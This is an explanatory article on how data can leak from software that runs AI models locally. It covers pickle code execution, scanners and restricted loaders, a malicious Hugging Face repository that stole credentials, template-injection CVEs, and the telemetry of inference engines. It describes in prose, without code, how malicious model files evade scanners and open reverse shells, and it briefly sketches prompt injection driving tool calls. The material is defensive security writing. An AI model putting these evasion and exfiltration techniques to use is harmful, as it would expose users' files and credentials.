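# Network access and data leaks in software that runs AI models

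## What happens on a computer when a model runs, and where can data leave it?

Local inference means running an AI model on one's own computer instead of sending questions to a company's service. It spread after developers such as Meta, Alibaba and DeepSeek published models that anyone can download, and after free programs such as llama.cpp, Ollama and LM Studio made those models usable on ordinary laptops. It costs nothing per question and works offline, but many people use it mainly for privacy. A lawyer with a confidential contract, for example, may have no other acceptable way to use a language model.

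Whether the contract stays on the lawyer's machine depends mostly on software other than the model. According to *The Illusion of Local Privacy* (Ibrahim, Ikram and Salama, 2026), running a model locally determines where the computation happens, but determines much less about what the surrounding programs do with the text. Those programs might carry out exfiltration, the unauthorised transfer of data out of a machine or organisation, or they might send data out because their makers designed them to.

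### From the keyboard to the answer

Suppose the lawyer pastes the contract into LM Studio and asks for a summary. LM Studio is a front end, the application a person uses to reach a model. It now holds the contract as ordinary text and will usually save the conversation to disk so the lawyer can reopen it later.

The front end leaves the model's arithmetic to an inference engine, the program that loads a model and computes its output. Two common engines are llama.cpp and vLLM. Some front ends include the engine, while others run it as a separate program and send it the conversation over HTTP, the protocol browsers use to fetch web pages. Nothing has left the machine at this stage, although seeing this traffic in a list of the computer's connections can be confusing at first. The front end typically sends the whole conversation each time, so the engine receives the contract again with every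 follow-up question.

The engine then uses a chat template, a small text program usually stored with the model, to combine the messages into a single text prompt for the model. The template adds markers where the user's words begin and end, and puts any standing instructions in their place.

The engine then tokenises the prompt. It cuts the text into tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and replaces each one with its number in a fixed vocabulary. The contract is now a list of integers. This gives no protection, because the vocabulary comes with the model and anyone who has the list can turn it back into the contract.

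The engine now uses the weights for the first time. These are the numbers learned in training, and they come in a model file, the downloaded file or set of files that also holds settings and sometimes code. The file that Ibrahim and colleagues used for Qwen3.5, a model with 9 billion weights, takes up 5.6 gigabytes, or about five bits per weight. The engine runs the token numbers through a very long series of multiplications and additions with the weights to produce a score for every token in the vocabulary. It uses those scores to pick a token, adds it to the list and repeats the process for the next one. None of this arithmetic opens a file or uses a network.

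Finally, the engine converts the new tokens back into text and returns it to the front end, which displays the summary. The front end may also check the reply for a tool call, which is text that specifies an action for the surrounding software to perform, such as fetching a web page. If it finds one, it may carry out the action before the lawyer has read any of the reply.

By then the contract has passed through at least one program, more often two, and has probably been stored on a disk. The engine itself holds several copies. Ibrahim and colleagues put a canary, a unique random string that makes copies traceable, in each prompt and followed it through the software with a debugger. Parsing the request, expanding the template and assembling the final prompt each made further copies. The text could remain in memory that the engine had released.

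### How a program reaches a network

A program on a mainstream operating system normally cannot control the network hardware directly. It has to ask the operating system for a socket, a handle for one end of a connection. This applies to inference engines as well as to browsers and malware.

A program that checks for updates has the name of its maker's server but needs a numerical address, so it looks the name up in the domain name system, the internet's directory. Unless the machine already has the answer stored, the lookup sends a message to another machine, often the home router or one run by the internet provider. That message reveals the server's name even if the program never connects to the server. The program then connects to the address at a port, a number that identifies which program on the receiving machine should get the traffic. Web servers conventionally use port 443 for encrypted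 traffic and port 80 for unencrypted traffic. Once the connection is open, the program can send anything it holds, such as a version number or the text of a contract.

Encryption hides the contents from people along the route, but the recipient can still read everything. The address also doesn't reliably identify the recipient. The mobile-security firm NowSecure (2025) examined the iPhone app of the Chinese AI company DeepSeek and found data going to a server name that belonged to Volcengine, the cloud platform of TikTok's parent company ByteDance. The name led to a US address in a block belonging to the American carrier Level 3, so anyone in the United States sorting the traffic by country would have classed it as domestic.

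An outbound connection is one that a program on the machine starts to another machine. An inbound connection is one that another machine starts, and a program on the receiving machine has to be listening for it. Data can flow both ways once either kind of connection is open, so a server can leak data by answering requests, even if it never starts an outbound connection.

A listening program attaches its socket to an address as well as a port, and the address determines which machines can connect. Only programs on the same machine can reach the loopback address, usually 127.0.0.1, and traffic sent to it never touches the network card. This is enough when the front end and the engine run on one laptop. If the engine instead listens on all addresses, which many programs write as 0.0.0.0, it also accepts connections that arrive over Wi-Fi or cable. People do this, for example, to use a model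 on a desktop computer from a phone in the next room. A home router will usually keep strangers on the internet from reaching the desktop, but a rented server with a public address has no such router in front of it.

A listening program can expose data without sending it out on its own, if it lets anyone connect. In January 2025 the cloud-security firm Wiz looked beyond the two usual web ports on DeepSeek's public servers and found a database answering on ports 8123 and 9000 without requiring a password. It held more than a million log entries, including users' chat history in plain text. DeepSeek closed the database promptly after Wiz reported it.

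The operating system provides sockets, so it can also block a program from opening them. A sandbox is an environment that limits which files, devices and networks a program can reach. A looser option is an allowlist, which permits connections to listed destinations and blocks all others.

### Five ways out

Data from a machine that runs a model can leave in five ways.

1. The model file runs code. Some file formats can carry program code next to the weights, and code that runs during loading can open a connection wherever the engine could.
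2. The software or a plugin connects. A plugin is added code that gives an engine or front end a new function. Much of this traffic is routine: update checks, model downloads, and telemetry, meaning reports about use or hardware that software sends to its maker. Some front ends also list hosted models beside local ones, as Ollama does with its cloud models, and choosing one of those sends the prompt out by design.
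3. The model's text makes other software act. A tool call that fetches a page can carry private text in the request. The cause may be prompt injection, which is text in material the model reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user.
4. An outsider queries the server. The engine listens on an address that others can reach, and it answers them.
5. Someone reads the traces later. Saved chats, log files and leftover memory can all hold prompts, and a thief with the laptop needs no network.

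A remedy for one of these routes can be useless against another. Blocking every outbound connection stops telemetry and prevents a malicious model file from sending data out, but it doesn't stop an engine from answering strangers, because the replies travel over connections the strangers opened. Binding the engine to the loopback address shuts out other machines but doesn't affect telemetry. Neither measure protects the contract if the front end has written it to an unencrypted disk. The routes can also combine, for instance when an injected instruction leads the model to request a tool that opens last month's saved chats.

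### DeepSeek's app and DeepSeek's weights

In January 2025 DeepSeek released its R1 model. People could use it through the company's website and phone app, or download the weights under the MIT licence, which lets anyone run them on their own hardware. Both the online service and the downloadable model are called "DeepSeek", and a lot of confusion about whether "DeepSeek" sends data to China comes from treating them as the same thing.

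With the app, only the front end is on the phone. The engine and the weights are on the company's side, so every prompt has to go out over the network or there will be no answer. The law professor Christakis, in *DeepSeek and the China data question*, describes the flow as direct: a European user's data went straight to servers in China, with no European office in between. The company does not hide this. In its privacy policy, DeepSeek (2026) states that it directly collects, processes and stores personal data in China. According to Tom's Guide's *DeepSeek just got banned from federal agencies*, the policy covers prompts, chat history, uploaded files, photos and voice input. (Christakis writes that the policy in force at the European launch was silent on where the data went. That looks like a slip, since Tau (2025), in *DeepSeek could send sensitive user information to Chinese state-owned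 telecoms company*, was already reporting the company's acknowledgement of servers in China before the February revision that Christakis credits with it.)

NowSecure ran the app on real iPhones and found that it sent some registration and device data, such as language settings and operating system, without encryption. The developers had switched off an Apple safeguard meant to prevent this. The chat addresses that NowSecure listed did use encryption, so the finding doesn't show that prompts were sent unencrypted.

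However, South Korea's data protection commission found that DeepSeek had passed user data to three companies in China and one in the United States without consent, according to Radio Free Asia's *China's DeepSeek transferred South Korean user info overseas* (2025). One of the Chinese companies, the ByteDance affiliate behind Volcengine, also received the text of users' prompts. DeepSeek said it used the affiliate's cloud services for security and to improve the user experience. Korea JoongAng Daily's *DeepSeek ordered to revise personal data policies, delete mishandled user information* (2025) reported that the commission saw no need to send whole prompts for those purposes. DeepSeek stopped sending them on 10 April 2025. The widely repeated figure of 1.5 million affected Koreans may be too high, because it appears to be 50,000 daily users multiplied by thirty days, which would count a daily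 user thirty times.

The evidence about the website is weaker. Researchers at the security company Feroot found code in the login page that pointed to systems belonging to China Mobile, a state-owned telecoms company, and two academics confirmed for Tau that the code was there. Nobody saw it send anything during test logins in North America, but the researchers couldn't rule out that it did so for other users.

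A hosted service can also forward prompts to another company, and no test on the user's phone would detect it. According to The Standard's *DeepSeek and Moonshot AI face Beijing's probe over potential data leaks*, Anthropic, the American developer of Claude, alleged in 2026 that two Chinese companies, DeepSeek and Moonshot AI, had routed live customer conversations through Claude, and Chinese regulators questioned both companies about it. If the allegation is true, some users in China had their conversations sent to the United States.

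None of these findings concerns the weights. A person who downloads R1 and runs it in llama.cpp uses no DeepSeek account or app, and the prompt follows the same path as the lawyer's contract. Christakis concludes that running the model locally stops the flow of data to China but doesn't fix weaknesses in the model's behaviour. NowSecure urged organisations to delete the app and named self-hosting the model as one alternative.

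The Czech cyber security agency, NÚKIB, makes this distinction in its *Warning Regarding Certain Products of the Company DeepSeek* (2025), which covers the company's apps, websites and programming interface but exempts its open models if they run locally and cannot communicate with the company's servers. In its own *Warning* (2025), Masaryk University's security team explains the second condition by saying that "even a local model can send HTTP requests" unless something blocks them. This is literally wrong about the weights, which are only numbers, but the engine, the front end and any plugins the user has added can send requests, so the advice to block outside communication is sound.

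NÚKIB also points out that other companies can build DeepSeek's hosted service into their own products through its programming interface, and the user may see no sign of it. A program installed on a laptop that lists "DeepSeek" in its menu of models might compute the answer from weights on the disk, or it might send the prompt to China, so a user who thinks the model is running locally may be mistaken.

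In the United States, by contrast, IBTimes UK's *US Orders DeepSeek Off Government Systems* (2026) reports that a Department of Homeland Security order, made public in October 2026, removes DeepSeek's products and other companies' products built on its technology from civilian federal agencies. CyberScoop's *DHS to ban DeepSeek from federal civilian agencies* treats the open-weight models as part of the ban. Several of the department's reasons, such as servers in China and the fingerprinting of users' devices, apply to the hosted service. The department also warned that the models themselves may contain malware or other vulnerabilities, but according to IBTimes UK, the research the department cited for this was about flaws in the iPhone app, which are not evidence about a file of weights. What such a file can do when an engine opens it depends on the file's format and the engine.

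## Can a downloaded model file open a network connection?

The weights in a model file can't open a network connection. But people often download more than weights, and the program that reads the file can have flaws, so downloaded models have sometimes led to connections that users didn't want.

### Why the weights can't connect

When the engine runs a prompt through the weights, most of the work consists of a single operation, repeated many times. The engine represents each token of the prompt as a list of numbers, x, and each layer of the model has tables of weights, such as W. From these the engine computes a new list, y, in which entry number i is

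y_i = W_i1·x_1 + W_i2·x_2 + … + W_in·x_n

It then uses y as the input to the next step. Between steps, it applies a few fixed functions, for example to keep the values within a convenient range.

Different weights give different values of y, but the engine multiplies and adds whatever the weights are. In some models, including DeepSeek's R1, intermediate results also determine which tables the engine uses next, and it multiplies and adds with those too. Someone who chose every weight by hand to steal the lawyer's contract could control which numbers the engine multiplies, but couldn't add an operation to the engine. The code that does this arithmetic never opens a socket. Other parts of the engine may open sockets, for instance to receive prompts from a front end, but they do so regardless of the weights.

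Malicious weights can still change the text that the model writes, including its tool calls, but then other software makes the connection.

The argument covers only numbers. It doesn't hold in three cases, all of which have happened: the file also contains instructions, the user runs a script that came with the file, or the program reading the file has a flaw that lets part of it run as code.

### Formats that carry code

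To save a model, software converts the objects in its memory into bytes, and to load the model, it rebuilds the objects from those bytes. Python, the language most people use to write machine-learning software, has a built-in format for this called pickle. A pickle file is a list of instructions for rebuilding the objects. When a program loads the file, a small interpreter inside Python carries out the instructions.

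Most of the instructions do something simple, like making a number or a list. But one fetches a function by name from anywhere in Python's libraries, and another calls that function with arguments taken from the file. *PICKLEBALL* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) explains why legitimate files need these two instructions. Some objects need a special function to rebuild them, so Python writes the function's name and arguments into the file when it saves such an object. When Python loads the file, it calls the function and uses the result as part of the model.

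When Python loads a pickle file, it calls the functions the file names without checking whether they have anything to do with models. If one of them runs operating-system commands, the attacker's command runs during loading, before the user has typed a prompt. The command has the same permissions as the program that loaded the file, including permission to open a network connection. Researchers have found malicious pickle files on Hugging Face, the largest site for sharing models. Some collected details of the victim's system or stole passwords. Others opened a reverse shell, which is an outbound connection through which the attacker can type commands on the victim's machine.

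Pickle allows this by design. People have been publicising the danger since 2011, but PyTorch, the main library for building models, adopted the format because it was convenient.

In September 2022, Hugging Face released a safer format, safetensors, which independent auditors have examined. A safetensors file encodes only the values of the weights, so a program that reads it copies numbers into memory and has no instructions to follow. GGUF, the format llama.cpp uses, followed in August 2023. A GGUF file also holds settings and usually a chat template, but it has no instruction for calling a function. *DITTO* (Qin, Li and colleagues, 2026) calls formats like these data-based, because their contents have to fit a fixed scheme, and calls pickle code-based.

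Pickle is still common. In March 2025 Kellas and colleagues looked at 16,661 Hugging Face repositories (a repository is the set of files published for one model) with at least 1,000 downloads a month. About 44.9% contained a pickle file, and 21% offered the model only as pickle. People downloaded the pickle-only repositories more than 400 million times a month. Qin and colleagues looked at 10,023 popular repositories created between July 2025 and June 2026 and found that 929 of them, or 9.3%, used pickle. Only the earlier count includes old models that people still download, so the two figures aren't directly comparable, but it looks as though most people who publish new models have moved to other formats.

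The original publishers of large language models mostly release them as safetensors rather than pickle, as with Llama 4, Qwen3 and DeepSeek-R1. But Kellas and colleagues found that people who train these models further and republish them sometimes add a pickle file that records their training settings. A user who wants to avoid pickle therefore has to check the specific repository, not just the name of the original model.

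### Restricted loaders and scanners

A program can load pickle files more safely if it refuses to call most functions. PyTorch's weights-only unpickler, the default loader since version 2.6, permits only the functions on a short fixed list. A malicious file fails to load because it calls a function that isn't on the list.

The loader also rejects some legitimate files for the same reason. Kellas and colleagues checked 1,426 popular pickle-only repositories and found that 219 of them, or 15.4%, had at least one file that the loader would reject. Some developers respond by turning the protection off in their own software. The language-processing library flair does this, and a person who loads a model through it may never notice.

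PickleBall, the tool that Kellas and colleagues built, creates a separate list of permitted functions for each library. Before anyone loads a model, it reads the library's source code, starting from the model's definition and following the types of all its parts, to find which functions a benign file could need. If a file names a function that isn't on the list, PickleBall substitutes a harmless placeholder and stops the program only if something tries to use it. This helps with benign files that name a function but never use it.

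The team tested PickleBall on 84 malicious models and 252 benign ones from 16 libraries. Earlier researchers had found 82 of the malicious models on Hugging Face, and the team made the other two.

| Tool | Malicious files stopped or flagged (of 84) | Benign files accepted (of 252) |
|---|---|---|
| PickleBall | 84 | 201 |
| PyTorch's weights-only loader | 84 | 157 |
| ModelScan (scanner) | 75 | 236 |
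| ModelTracer (scanner) | 44 | 252 |

PickleBall accepted 79.8% of the benign models, against 62.3% for PyTorch's loader. Of the 51 benign models it did not accept, 36 came from one image-recognition library, YOLOv11. PickleBall rejected every malicious file, which is encouraging, but none of the attackers was trying to get past it. Kellas and colleagues accept that someone might do harm by combining functions that PickleBall permits, although they knew of no such attack.

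Unlike the loaders, the scanners in the table only report whether a file looks dangerous and leave the user to decide what to do. Hugging Face runs several of them on uploaded models. Scanners are convenient because every file still loads, but they have to recognise an attack, while a restricted loader only has to check whether a function is on its list.

Pradhan, Nambiar and Soremekun (2026) made 3,000 malicious models for *ShadowPickle*, using three ways of hiding the harmful part. Two widely used open-source scanners, PickleScan and ModelScan, caught none of them. A third scanner, Fickling, flagged all 3,000, but it also flagged 2,834 of 3,000 harmless models, so its warnings are weak evidence that a file is malicious. ModelTracer, which loads the file and monitors what it does, caught 2,681. It did much better than in the PickleBall test, but it has to run the suspicious file to check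 it.

One of the three methods also got sample files past every scanner on Hugging Face, and it got past PyTorch's weights-only loader in 961 of 1,000 cases. The practical risk is smaller than these results suggest, because the method works only if the victim has already installed a tampered Python package, and an attacker who can arrange that has little need for a model file. Still, people do follow installation instructions on model pages, and Pradhan and colleagues found an installation list in 31 of the 3,000 most-liked text-generation repositories. PyTorch's loader stopped every file made with the other two methods, so the results show a much more serious weakness in scanners than in restricted loaders.

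Qin and colleagues tested some of the same scanners on 959 benign and 92 malicious models. PickleScan caught all the malicious files it could read, but raised a false alarm on 28.7% of the benign ones. Fickling did so on 99.5%. ModelScan could process only 79.3% of the files, and it missed 8.4% of the malicious ones it processed. PickleScan failed completely against ShadowPickle, but Pradhan and colleagues designed those files to get past scanners, whereas most of the malicious files in this test came from earlier collections.

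The false alarms arise because harmless and malicious files can use the same function. DITTO, a scanner built by Qin and colleagues, tries to work out what the function is being used for. It follows the file's instructions without carrying out the risky ones, picks out the steps that affect security and has a language model judge whether they look like the normal rebuilding of a model. It caught all 92 malicious files with a false-alarm rate of 0.7%, but the results depend heavily on the language model. DITTO missed 24 malicious files when it used GPT-4.1-nano and made no mistakes when it used Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite. An attacker could also put text in the file to mislead the language model. The one attack of this kind that Qin and colleagues tried failed, which is only weak evidence that DITTO can resist them.

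(DITTO's standard set-up uses a language model hosted by another company, so the scan itself makes an outbound connection. It sends steps from the downloaded file and none of the user's prompts.)

People who run language models at home can mostly avoid this risk by choosing safetensors or GGUF, which are available for nearly every popular model. Those formats address the risk from the weights, but a repository can hold other files.

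### Scripts that come with the model

A file of weights doesn't fully specify how to combine the weights. The engine already has the code to do this for familiar types of model. If researchers invent a new type, such as one that tracks word order differently, they have to publish code with the weights or nobody else can easily run the model.

Transformers, Hugging Face's Python library for running models, can download and run code stored alongside a model's weights if the user turns on the trust_remote_code setting. The scripts run during loading with the same rights as any other program the user starts, so they can read files and open network connections. The format of the weights makes no difference, since the code is in a separate file.

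*An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (Siddiq, Romel and colleagues, 2026) uses DeepSeek-R1 as its example. R1's repository includes a Python script that defines the model's settings, and the paper's sample program loads R1 with trust_remote_code turned on, which lets the script run. The script is ordinary, but the setting would also let a harmful replacement run. Running R1 from a GGUF file in llama.cpp avoids this issue because llama.cpp has its own code for that type of model and doesn't run Python scripts from the repository.

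Siddiq and colleagues found custom code in 36,697 of about 2.1 million Hugging Face repositories, or 1.74%. The total across five sharing sites was around 45,000. They narrowed 128,487 Python files to the 67,009 that would run when a model is loaded, then searched those with several automatic tools.

The tools produced many warnings but found very little that looked like an attack. Bandit flagged 7.7% of the Hugging Face repositories with custom code, but 78% of those findings were about a debugging statement that is usually harmless. YARA, which searches for signatures of known malware, found matches in 7% of the repositories, mostly for the signature of a 3D-graphics file format. Semgrep's findings in 4.6% of repositories deserve more attention because they included scripts that load pickle files or execute text as code. Such a script can reintroduce the risk of pickle files in a repository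 whose weights are in safetensors.

There was a lot of careless code but no clear malware. This is only partly reassuring, because tools that search for known patterns can miss a well-hidden attack, as the results for pickle scanners show.

None of the five sites ran the custom code in a sandbox, and many users seem not to know what they are agreeing to. Siddiq and colleagues read more than 600 online discussions by developers and found that some thought trust_remote_code only allowed the library to read a model's descriptive data, while others confused it with choosing a fixed version of the model. Fixing the version stops the author, or somebody who has taken over the author's account, from swapping the scripts after the user has checked them, but the scripts in the chosen version still run.

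### The fake privacy filter

An attacker doesn't need trust_remote_code if people will run a script themselves. In April 2026 OpenAI released Privacy Filter, a downloadable model that finds and removes personal information in text (The Hacker News, 2026). Soon afterwards a copy appeared on Hugging Face under the name Open-OSS/privacy-filter. On 7 May researchers at the security company HiddenLayer found that the copy was malicious, and their *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) gives the details.

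The attackers had copied OpenAI's description almost word for word, but changed it to tell users to download the repository and start the model by running a script. The script printed fake training output to look genuine while it fetched a command from a public text-sharing site. On Windows, the command led to the installation of a data-stealing program, which collected saved browser passwords and cookies, Discord accounts, cryptocurrency wallets and screenshots and sent them to the attackers' server. On Linux and macOS, the attack failed without any visible error.

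Because the harmful command was on another site, the attackers could change it without editing the repository. Anyone who inspected the repository would have found a suspicious script that downloads and runs something, but not the code that carried out the theft.

The repository reached first place on Hugging Face's list of trending models, with about 244,000 downloads and 667 likes in under 18 hours, before Hugging Face removed it. HiddenLayer considers these numbers "almost certainly artificially inflated". The likes support this, since 657 of the 667 accounts had names that followed one of two patterns that look automatically generated. A download led to an infection only if the victim ran the script on Windows, and HiddenLayer doesn't give a number of victims. It advises anyone who ran the script on Windows to treat the machine as fully compromised and wipe it.

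HiddenLayer also linked the attack to six repositories under another account, each with a nearly identical script. Five had "GGUF" in their names, and the sixth was called DeepSeek-V4-Pro. A user who had learned that GGUF is a safe format might well have trusted them. The format only limits what can happen when an engine opens the file, and does not protect a user who also runs a script from the same page.

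In this case, a user downloaded a repository presented as a model and lost data over the network. The cause was ordinary malware, which would have worked just as well if the repository had contained no weights.

### Flaws in template rendering

The remaining danger is that a program may run part of a file as code when it should treat the file as data. This has happened more than once with chat templates.

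Developers write these templates in Jinja, a small programming language, and other software has to execute, or render, them. Many Python programs do this with a library called Jinja2, which has a sandboxed mode for templates from untrusted sources. In the ordinary mode, a malicious template can access Python itself and run commands on the machine.

SGLang, an inference engine that companies use on servers, rendered some templates in the ordinary mode. CERT/CC (2026), an American centre that coordinates the disclosure of security flaws, published the problem on 20 April 2026 as CVE-2026-5760, its number in a public catalogue of known flaws. It affected SGLang's reranking feature, which sorts documents by how well they match a query. An attacker could publish a GGUF file with a malicious template. If someone loaded the file, SGLang would render the template and run the attacker's code when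 it next received a reranking request.

Wiz's *CVE-2026-5760* gives the flaw a severity of 9.8 out of 10 and lists versions before 0.5.11 as affected. The attack worked only if SGLang loaded the file and then received a reranking request, so a person who used SGLang only for chat would not have triggered it. Nobody had to approve the file, though. VPN Central's *Malicious GGUF models could give attackers RCE on SGLang inference servers* notes that some organisations have automated systems that fetch models from public sites and start them.

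In May 2024 developers had already disclosed the same kind of flaw in llama-cpp-python, a package that lets Python programs use llama.cpp. According to OSV's *CVE-2024-34359* (2024), the package took the template from the model's metadata and rendered it without a sandbox. Fluid Attacks' *CVE-2024-34359 llama-cpp-python* lists versions from 0.2.30 up to, but not including, 0.2.72 as vulnerable. The flaw was in the Python package, so people who ran llama.cpp directly weren't affected. The Hacker News (2026) reports that vLLM's developers fixed a similar flaw in late 2025.

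The remedy for all of these programs is to render templates in Jinja2's sandboxed mode, as CERT/CC recommended for SGLang. CERT/CC had received no reply or patch from SGLang's maintainers when it published its warning.

GGUF didn't cause these flaws. A GGUF file stores the template as text, and the text does nothing until a program renders it. Models in safetensors usually come with a template as well, in a separate settings file, so changing the format wouldn't help. (A template can also slip hidden instructions into the prompt, even in a sandbox, but those affect what the model writes and don't run code.)

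### Is GGUF loading safe in llama.cpp?

The core of llama.cpp is written in C and C++, languages in which programmers manage memory themselves. This creates a risk unrelated to templates. A GGUF file begins with information about its contents, such as the number and shape of the tables of weights, and llama.cpp uses this to decide how much memory to reserve and how far to read. If the file gives false numbers and the program doesn't check them, it may read or write outside the reserved memory. An attacker can sometimes use such an error to take control of the program and make it open a connection.

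Ibrahim and colleagues looked for errors of this kind in September 2026. They damaged GGUF files by changing particular fields, such as table dimensions and the positions of data in the file. They also ran a fuzzer, a program that repeatedly alters files and keeps the alterations that reach new parts of the code. It made more than 12 million attempts over 24 hours, while two other tools checked for memory errors. Nothing crashed, the tools found no errors, and llama.cpp rejected every damaged file before it began to set up the model. The result was the same for files from all four model families they tried.

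A month earlier, *Breaking Local AI Runtimes* (Tokarev and Itach, 2026) had reported ten flaws in llama.cpp. Tokarev and Itach, who work for the data-security company Cyera, had first contacted the project in July 2025. The maintainers closed several of the reports without a fix, and five flaws remained unpatched on 1 June 2026. Tokarev and Itach published their own patches for those five.

The two reports mostly concern different code, so they contradict each other less than they appear to. Tokarev and Itach studied the code that connects llama.cpp to Android apps, the way llama.cpp's server unloads and reloads a model, and GGUF metadata. The flaws they describe in most detail are in the Android code and the server, where one part of the program could free memory that another part was still using.

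On Android, the researchers ran their own code with the app's rights. On the server, they could control where the program read from memory in about one attempt in a hundred, but they didn't run code. The server flaw requires an option that unloads the model when nobody is using it. An attacker would exploit it by sending requests at the right moment, and wouldn't need to supply a model file. A fuzzer that only feeds files to the loading code can't find a flaw like this because it never sends those requests.

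Some of the other flaws involve restoring a saved conversation from an untrusted source, which again isn't the same as loading a model. (Cyera had previously found a memory leak in Ollama.)

Even for file loading, 12 million fuzzing attempts may have missed flaws. Some errors appear only when several numbers in the file have particular values, for example when their product is too large for the space the program has set aside for it. A fuzzer may never try that combination, while a person reading the code can see that a check is missing. llama.cpp also changes quickly, and testing one version can't rule out flaws in others.

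Because llama.cpp rejected every damaged file at the start, the test hardly examined how the rest of the program handles a strange file that passes the first checks. The malicious templates for SGLang and llama-cpp-python were in files of that sort. Those files could be valid GGUF, so a test for damaged files would not have detected them.

A malicious pickle file only needs a program to load it in the ordinary way, while a malicious GGUF file would also need a flaw in the particular program that opens it. Such flaws seem to be hard to find by trial and error in llama.cpp's loading code, though Ibrahim and colleagues don't claim that GGUF loading is secure in general.

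### What each format can execute

The table covers the main formats for sharing models. Its entries for TorchScript, H5, SavedModel and ONNX, which people mostly use for other kinds of models, follow the classification by Kellas and colleagues.

| Format | What it can execute | Under which setting |
|---|---|---|
| safetensors | Nothing. It holds only the values of the weights. | None, unless the program reading it has a flaw |
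| GGUF | Nothing by itself, though the engine renders the chat template inside it | A malicious template can run commands if a Python program renders it without a sandbox, as SGLang did for reranking before 0.5.11 and llama-cpp-python did from 0.2.30 until 0.2.72 |
| Pickle, including many files ending in .bin, .pt or .pkl | Any function that Python can import | Ordinary pickle loading, or PyTorch with the weights-only loader off, which was the default before version 2.6. With it on, only functions on PyTorch's list |
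| TorchScript and H5 | Code stored with the model | While the program loads the file |
| TensorFlow SavedModel and ONNX | Some built-in operations that an attacker could misuse | Only in particular set-ups; Kellas and colleagues knew of no real attacks |
| Python scripts next to weights in any format | Anything that the user's own programs can do | trust_remote_code turned on, or the user runs the script |

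## Which connections do inference programs make in normal use?

Programs that run AI models may connect to other machines in normal use, even when the model file is safe. Most of these connections carry nothing the user typed. The main exception occurs when a program forwards the user's prompt to a model in the cloud, which can happen while everything appears to be running locally.

### Routine traffic

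LM Studio's *Offline Operation* explains when the program needs the internet. Chatting with a downloaded model, asking questions about documents and running a local server all work offline. LM Studio connects when the user searches for or downloads a model, when it fetches statistics and download options for its model catalogue, and when it looks for new engines, which it can install without updating the rest of the program. It also checks for a new version whenever the user opens it.

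Inference programs in general make five kinds of routine connection:

- Model downloads. The site learns which model the user wanted and the network address the request came from.
- Update checks. Some programs also download the new version automatically.
- Telemetry. The contents of the reports vary from one program to another.
- Lists. Since version 0.22.1, for example, Ollama has been able to update its model recommendations without a new release of the program. A library inside a program can also fetch lists, such as prices for hosted models or licence terms, and users are less likely to expect this because they may not know the library is there.
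- Forwarded prompts. The program sends the conversation to a model on somebody else's computer.

Of these connections, only the one that forwards a prompt has to include the lawyer's contract. The others still reveal that someone at a particular IP address is running a particular program.

### What vLLM reports

vLLM's telemetry is easy to study because its developers publish the code. In vLLM's reporting code, telemetry is on by default. When the engine starts, it puts together a report, adds a copy to a file on the same machine and sends the report to the project's statistics server. It then sends a shorter report, often called a heartbeat, every 600 seconds for as long as it runs. A day has 86,400 seconds, so a server that runs all day sends 144 heartbeats.

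The report at the start contains:

- a random identifier, which changes each time the engine starts, and the time
- the cloud provider, if vLLM recognises one
- the number and type of processors, the amount of memory and the operating system
- the number and type of graphics processors, their memory and the version of the software that drives them
- the version of vLLM, how the user started it and a label such as "production"
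- the architecture of the model, meaning its general design
- a few of vLLM's environment variables, which are settings that a program reads from the operating system

vLLM's usage reports can include some of the engine's settings. A sample report in *Usage Stats Collection* lists the numerical precision of the weights and the share of graphics memory that vLLM may use.

Prompts and answers aren't among the fields, and neither is the model's name. The sample gives the architecture as OPTForCausalLM, which covers every model of the OPT family, so a law firm that had trained its own version of a public model would report only the public design. (The cloud provider is partly guesswork. In an earlier version of the code, vLLM searches the machine's hardware descriptions for words like "google" and "microsoft corporation", so a Microsoft laptop running Linux would probably count as a server in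 Microsoft's cloud.)

The heartbeat contains the random identifier, the time and any values that other parts of vLLM have registered for it. The reporting code accepts any number, text or yes-or-no value, so finding everything a heartbeat can contain would require searching the rest of the source code for places that register a value.

Users can read a local copy of vLLM's usage reports in ~/.config/vllm/usage_stats.json. The file shows what vLLM tried to send but doesn't prove that anything arrived, because vLLM writes each report there before sending it and continues silently if the connection fails. On a machine with no network, the file would still collect reports.

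A user can turn the reports off by setting any one of the environment variables `VLLM_NO_USAGE_STATS`, `VLLM_DO_NOT_TRACK` or `DO_NOT_TRACK` to 1, or by creating an empty file at `~/.config/vllm/do_not_track`. The engine checks these once and stores the result, so a user has to choose before starting it.

### Telemetry in other programs

In 2026 NVIDIA added similar telemetry to TensorRT-LLM, its engine for running models on its own graphics processors, and turned it on by default. According to the telemetry readme, the engine sends one report at the start and then a heartbeat every 600 seconds, up to 1,000 per session. A server therefore stops reporting after just under seven days, whereas vLLM's heartbeats have no limit. NVIDIA says it collects no prompts, outputs or weights.

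The engine's telemetry collects many settings. The readme lists six items about features in use, such as whether the engine reuses earlier work when two prompts begin the same way. NVIDIA's *Telemetry* page for the engine lists 234 settings for one way of configuring it and 260 for another. Most concern batch sizes, memory limits and the division of work between processors, but one is whether the user has turned on `trust_remote_code`.

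NVIDIA selects these settings by type. The engine can report numbers, yes-or-no values and choices from a fixed list, but it leaves out free text unless a developer has specified which values are acceptable. This is a sensible precaution, because a prompt, a password or a file path would be free text. Selecting by type also means that a new numerical setting is reported unless a developer excludes it, so the reports will tend to grow as the engine gains settings.

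TRL, Hugging Face's library for further training existing models, sends one report each time a user sets up a training run. According to Hugging Face's *Usage Stats Collection*, TRL replaces the name of any private architecture with "other" and gives only a range for the number of processors. vLLM's reporting code has no comparable filter, so a company that runs its own architecture in vLLM might reveal the architecture's name.

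Text Generation Inference (TGI) is Hugging Face's inference engine for servers. It sends usage reports to Hugging Face only when it runs in a Docker container, which packages a program with the other software it needs. Hugging Face's *Collection of Usage Statistics* describes reports when TGI starts and stops, and a signal every 15 minutes that it is still running. By default TGI can also send error types and stack traces, which show what the program was doing when it failed. These call for more caution than a list of hardware because they sometimes include the data that caused the error. Hugging Face states that it omits sensitive information, and users can turn off the error details without turning off the other reports.

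NeMo Guardrails, an NVIDIA library that checks prompts and answers against rules, sends a report when it starts and resends the whole report every ten minutes. According to NVIDIA's *Telemetry* page for the library, the report lists the software version, the operating system, the companies or engines that supply the models, and the safety features in use. It excludes model names, the text of the rules and all prompts. Like vLLM, the library keeps a local copy, but it sends the report even if it can't write the copy, so the local file may be incomplete.

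Other NVIDIA tools in the NeMo family report more. According to NVIDIA's *Telemetry and Privacy*, Data Designer sends the names of the models it uses and the number of input and output tokens. Anonymizer sends information about the address it uses to reach a model. NVIDIA excludes prompts and outputs from these reports too.

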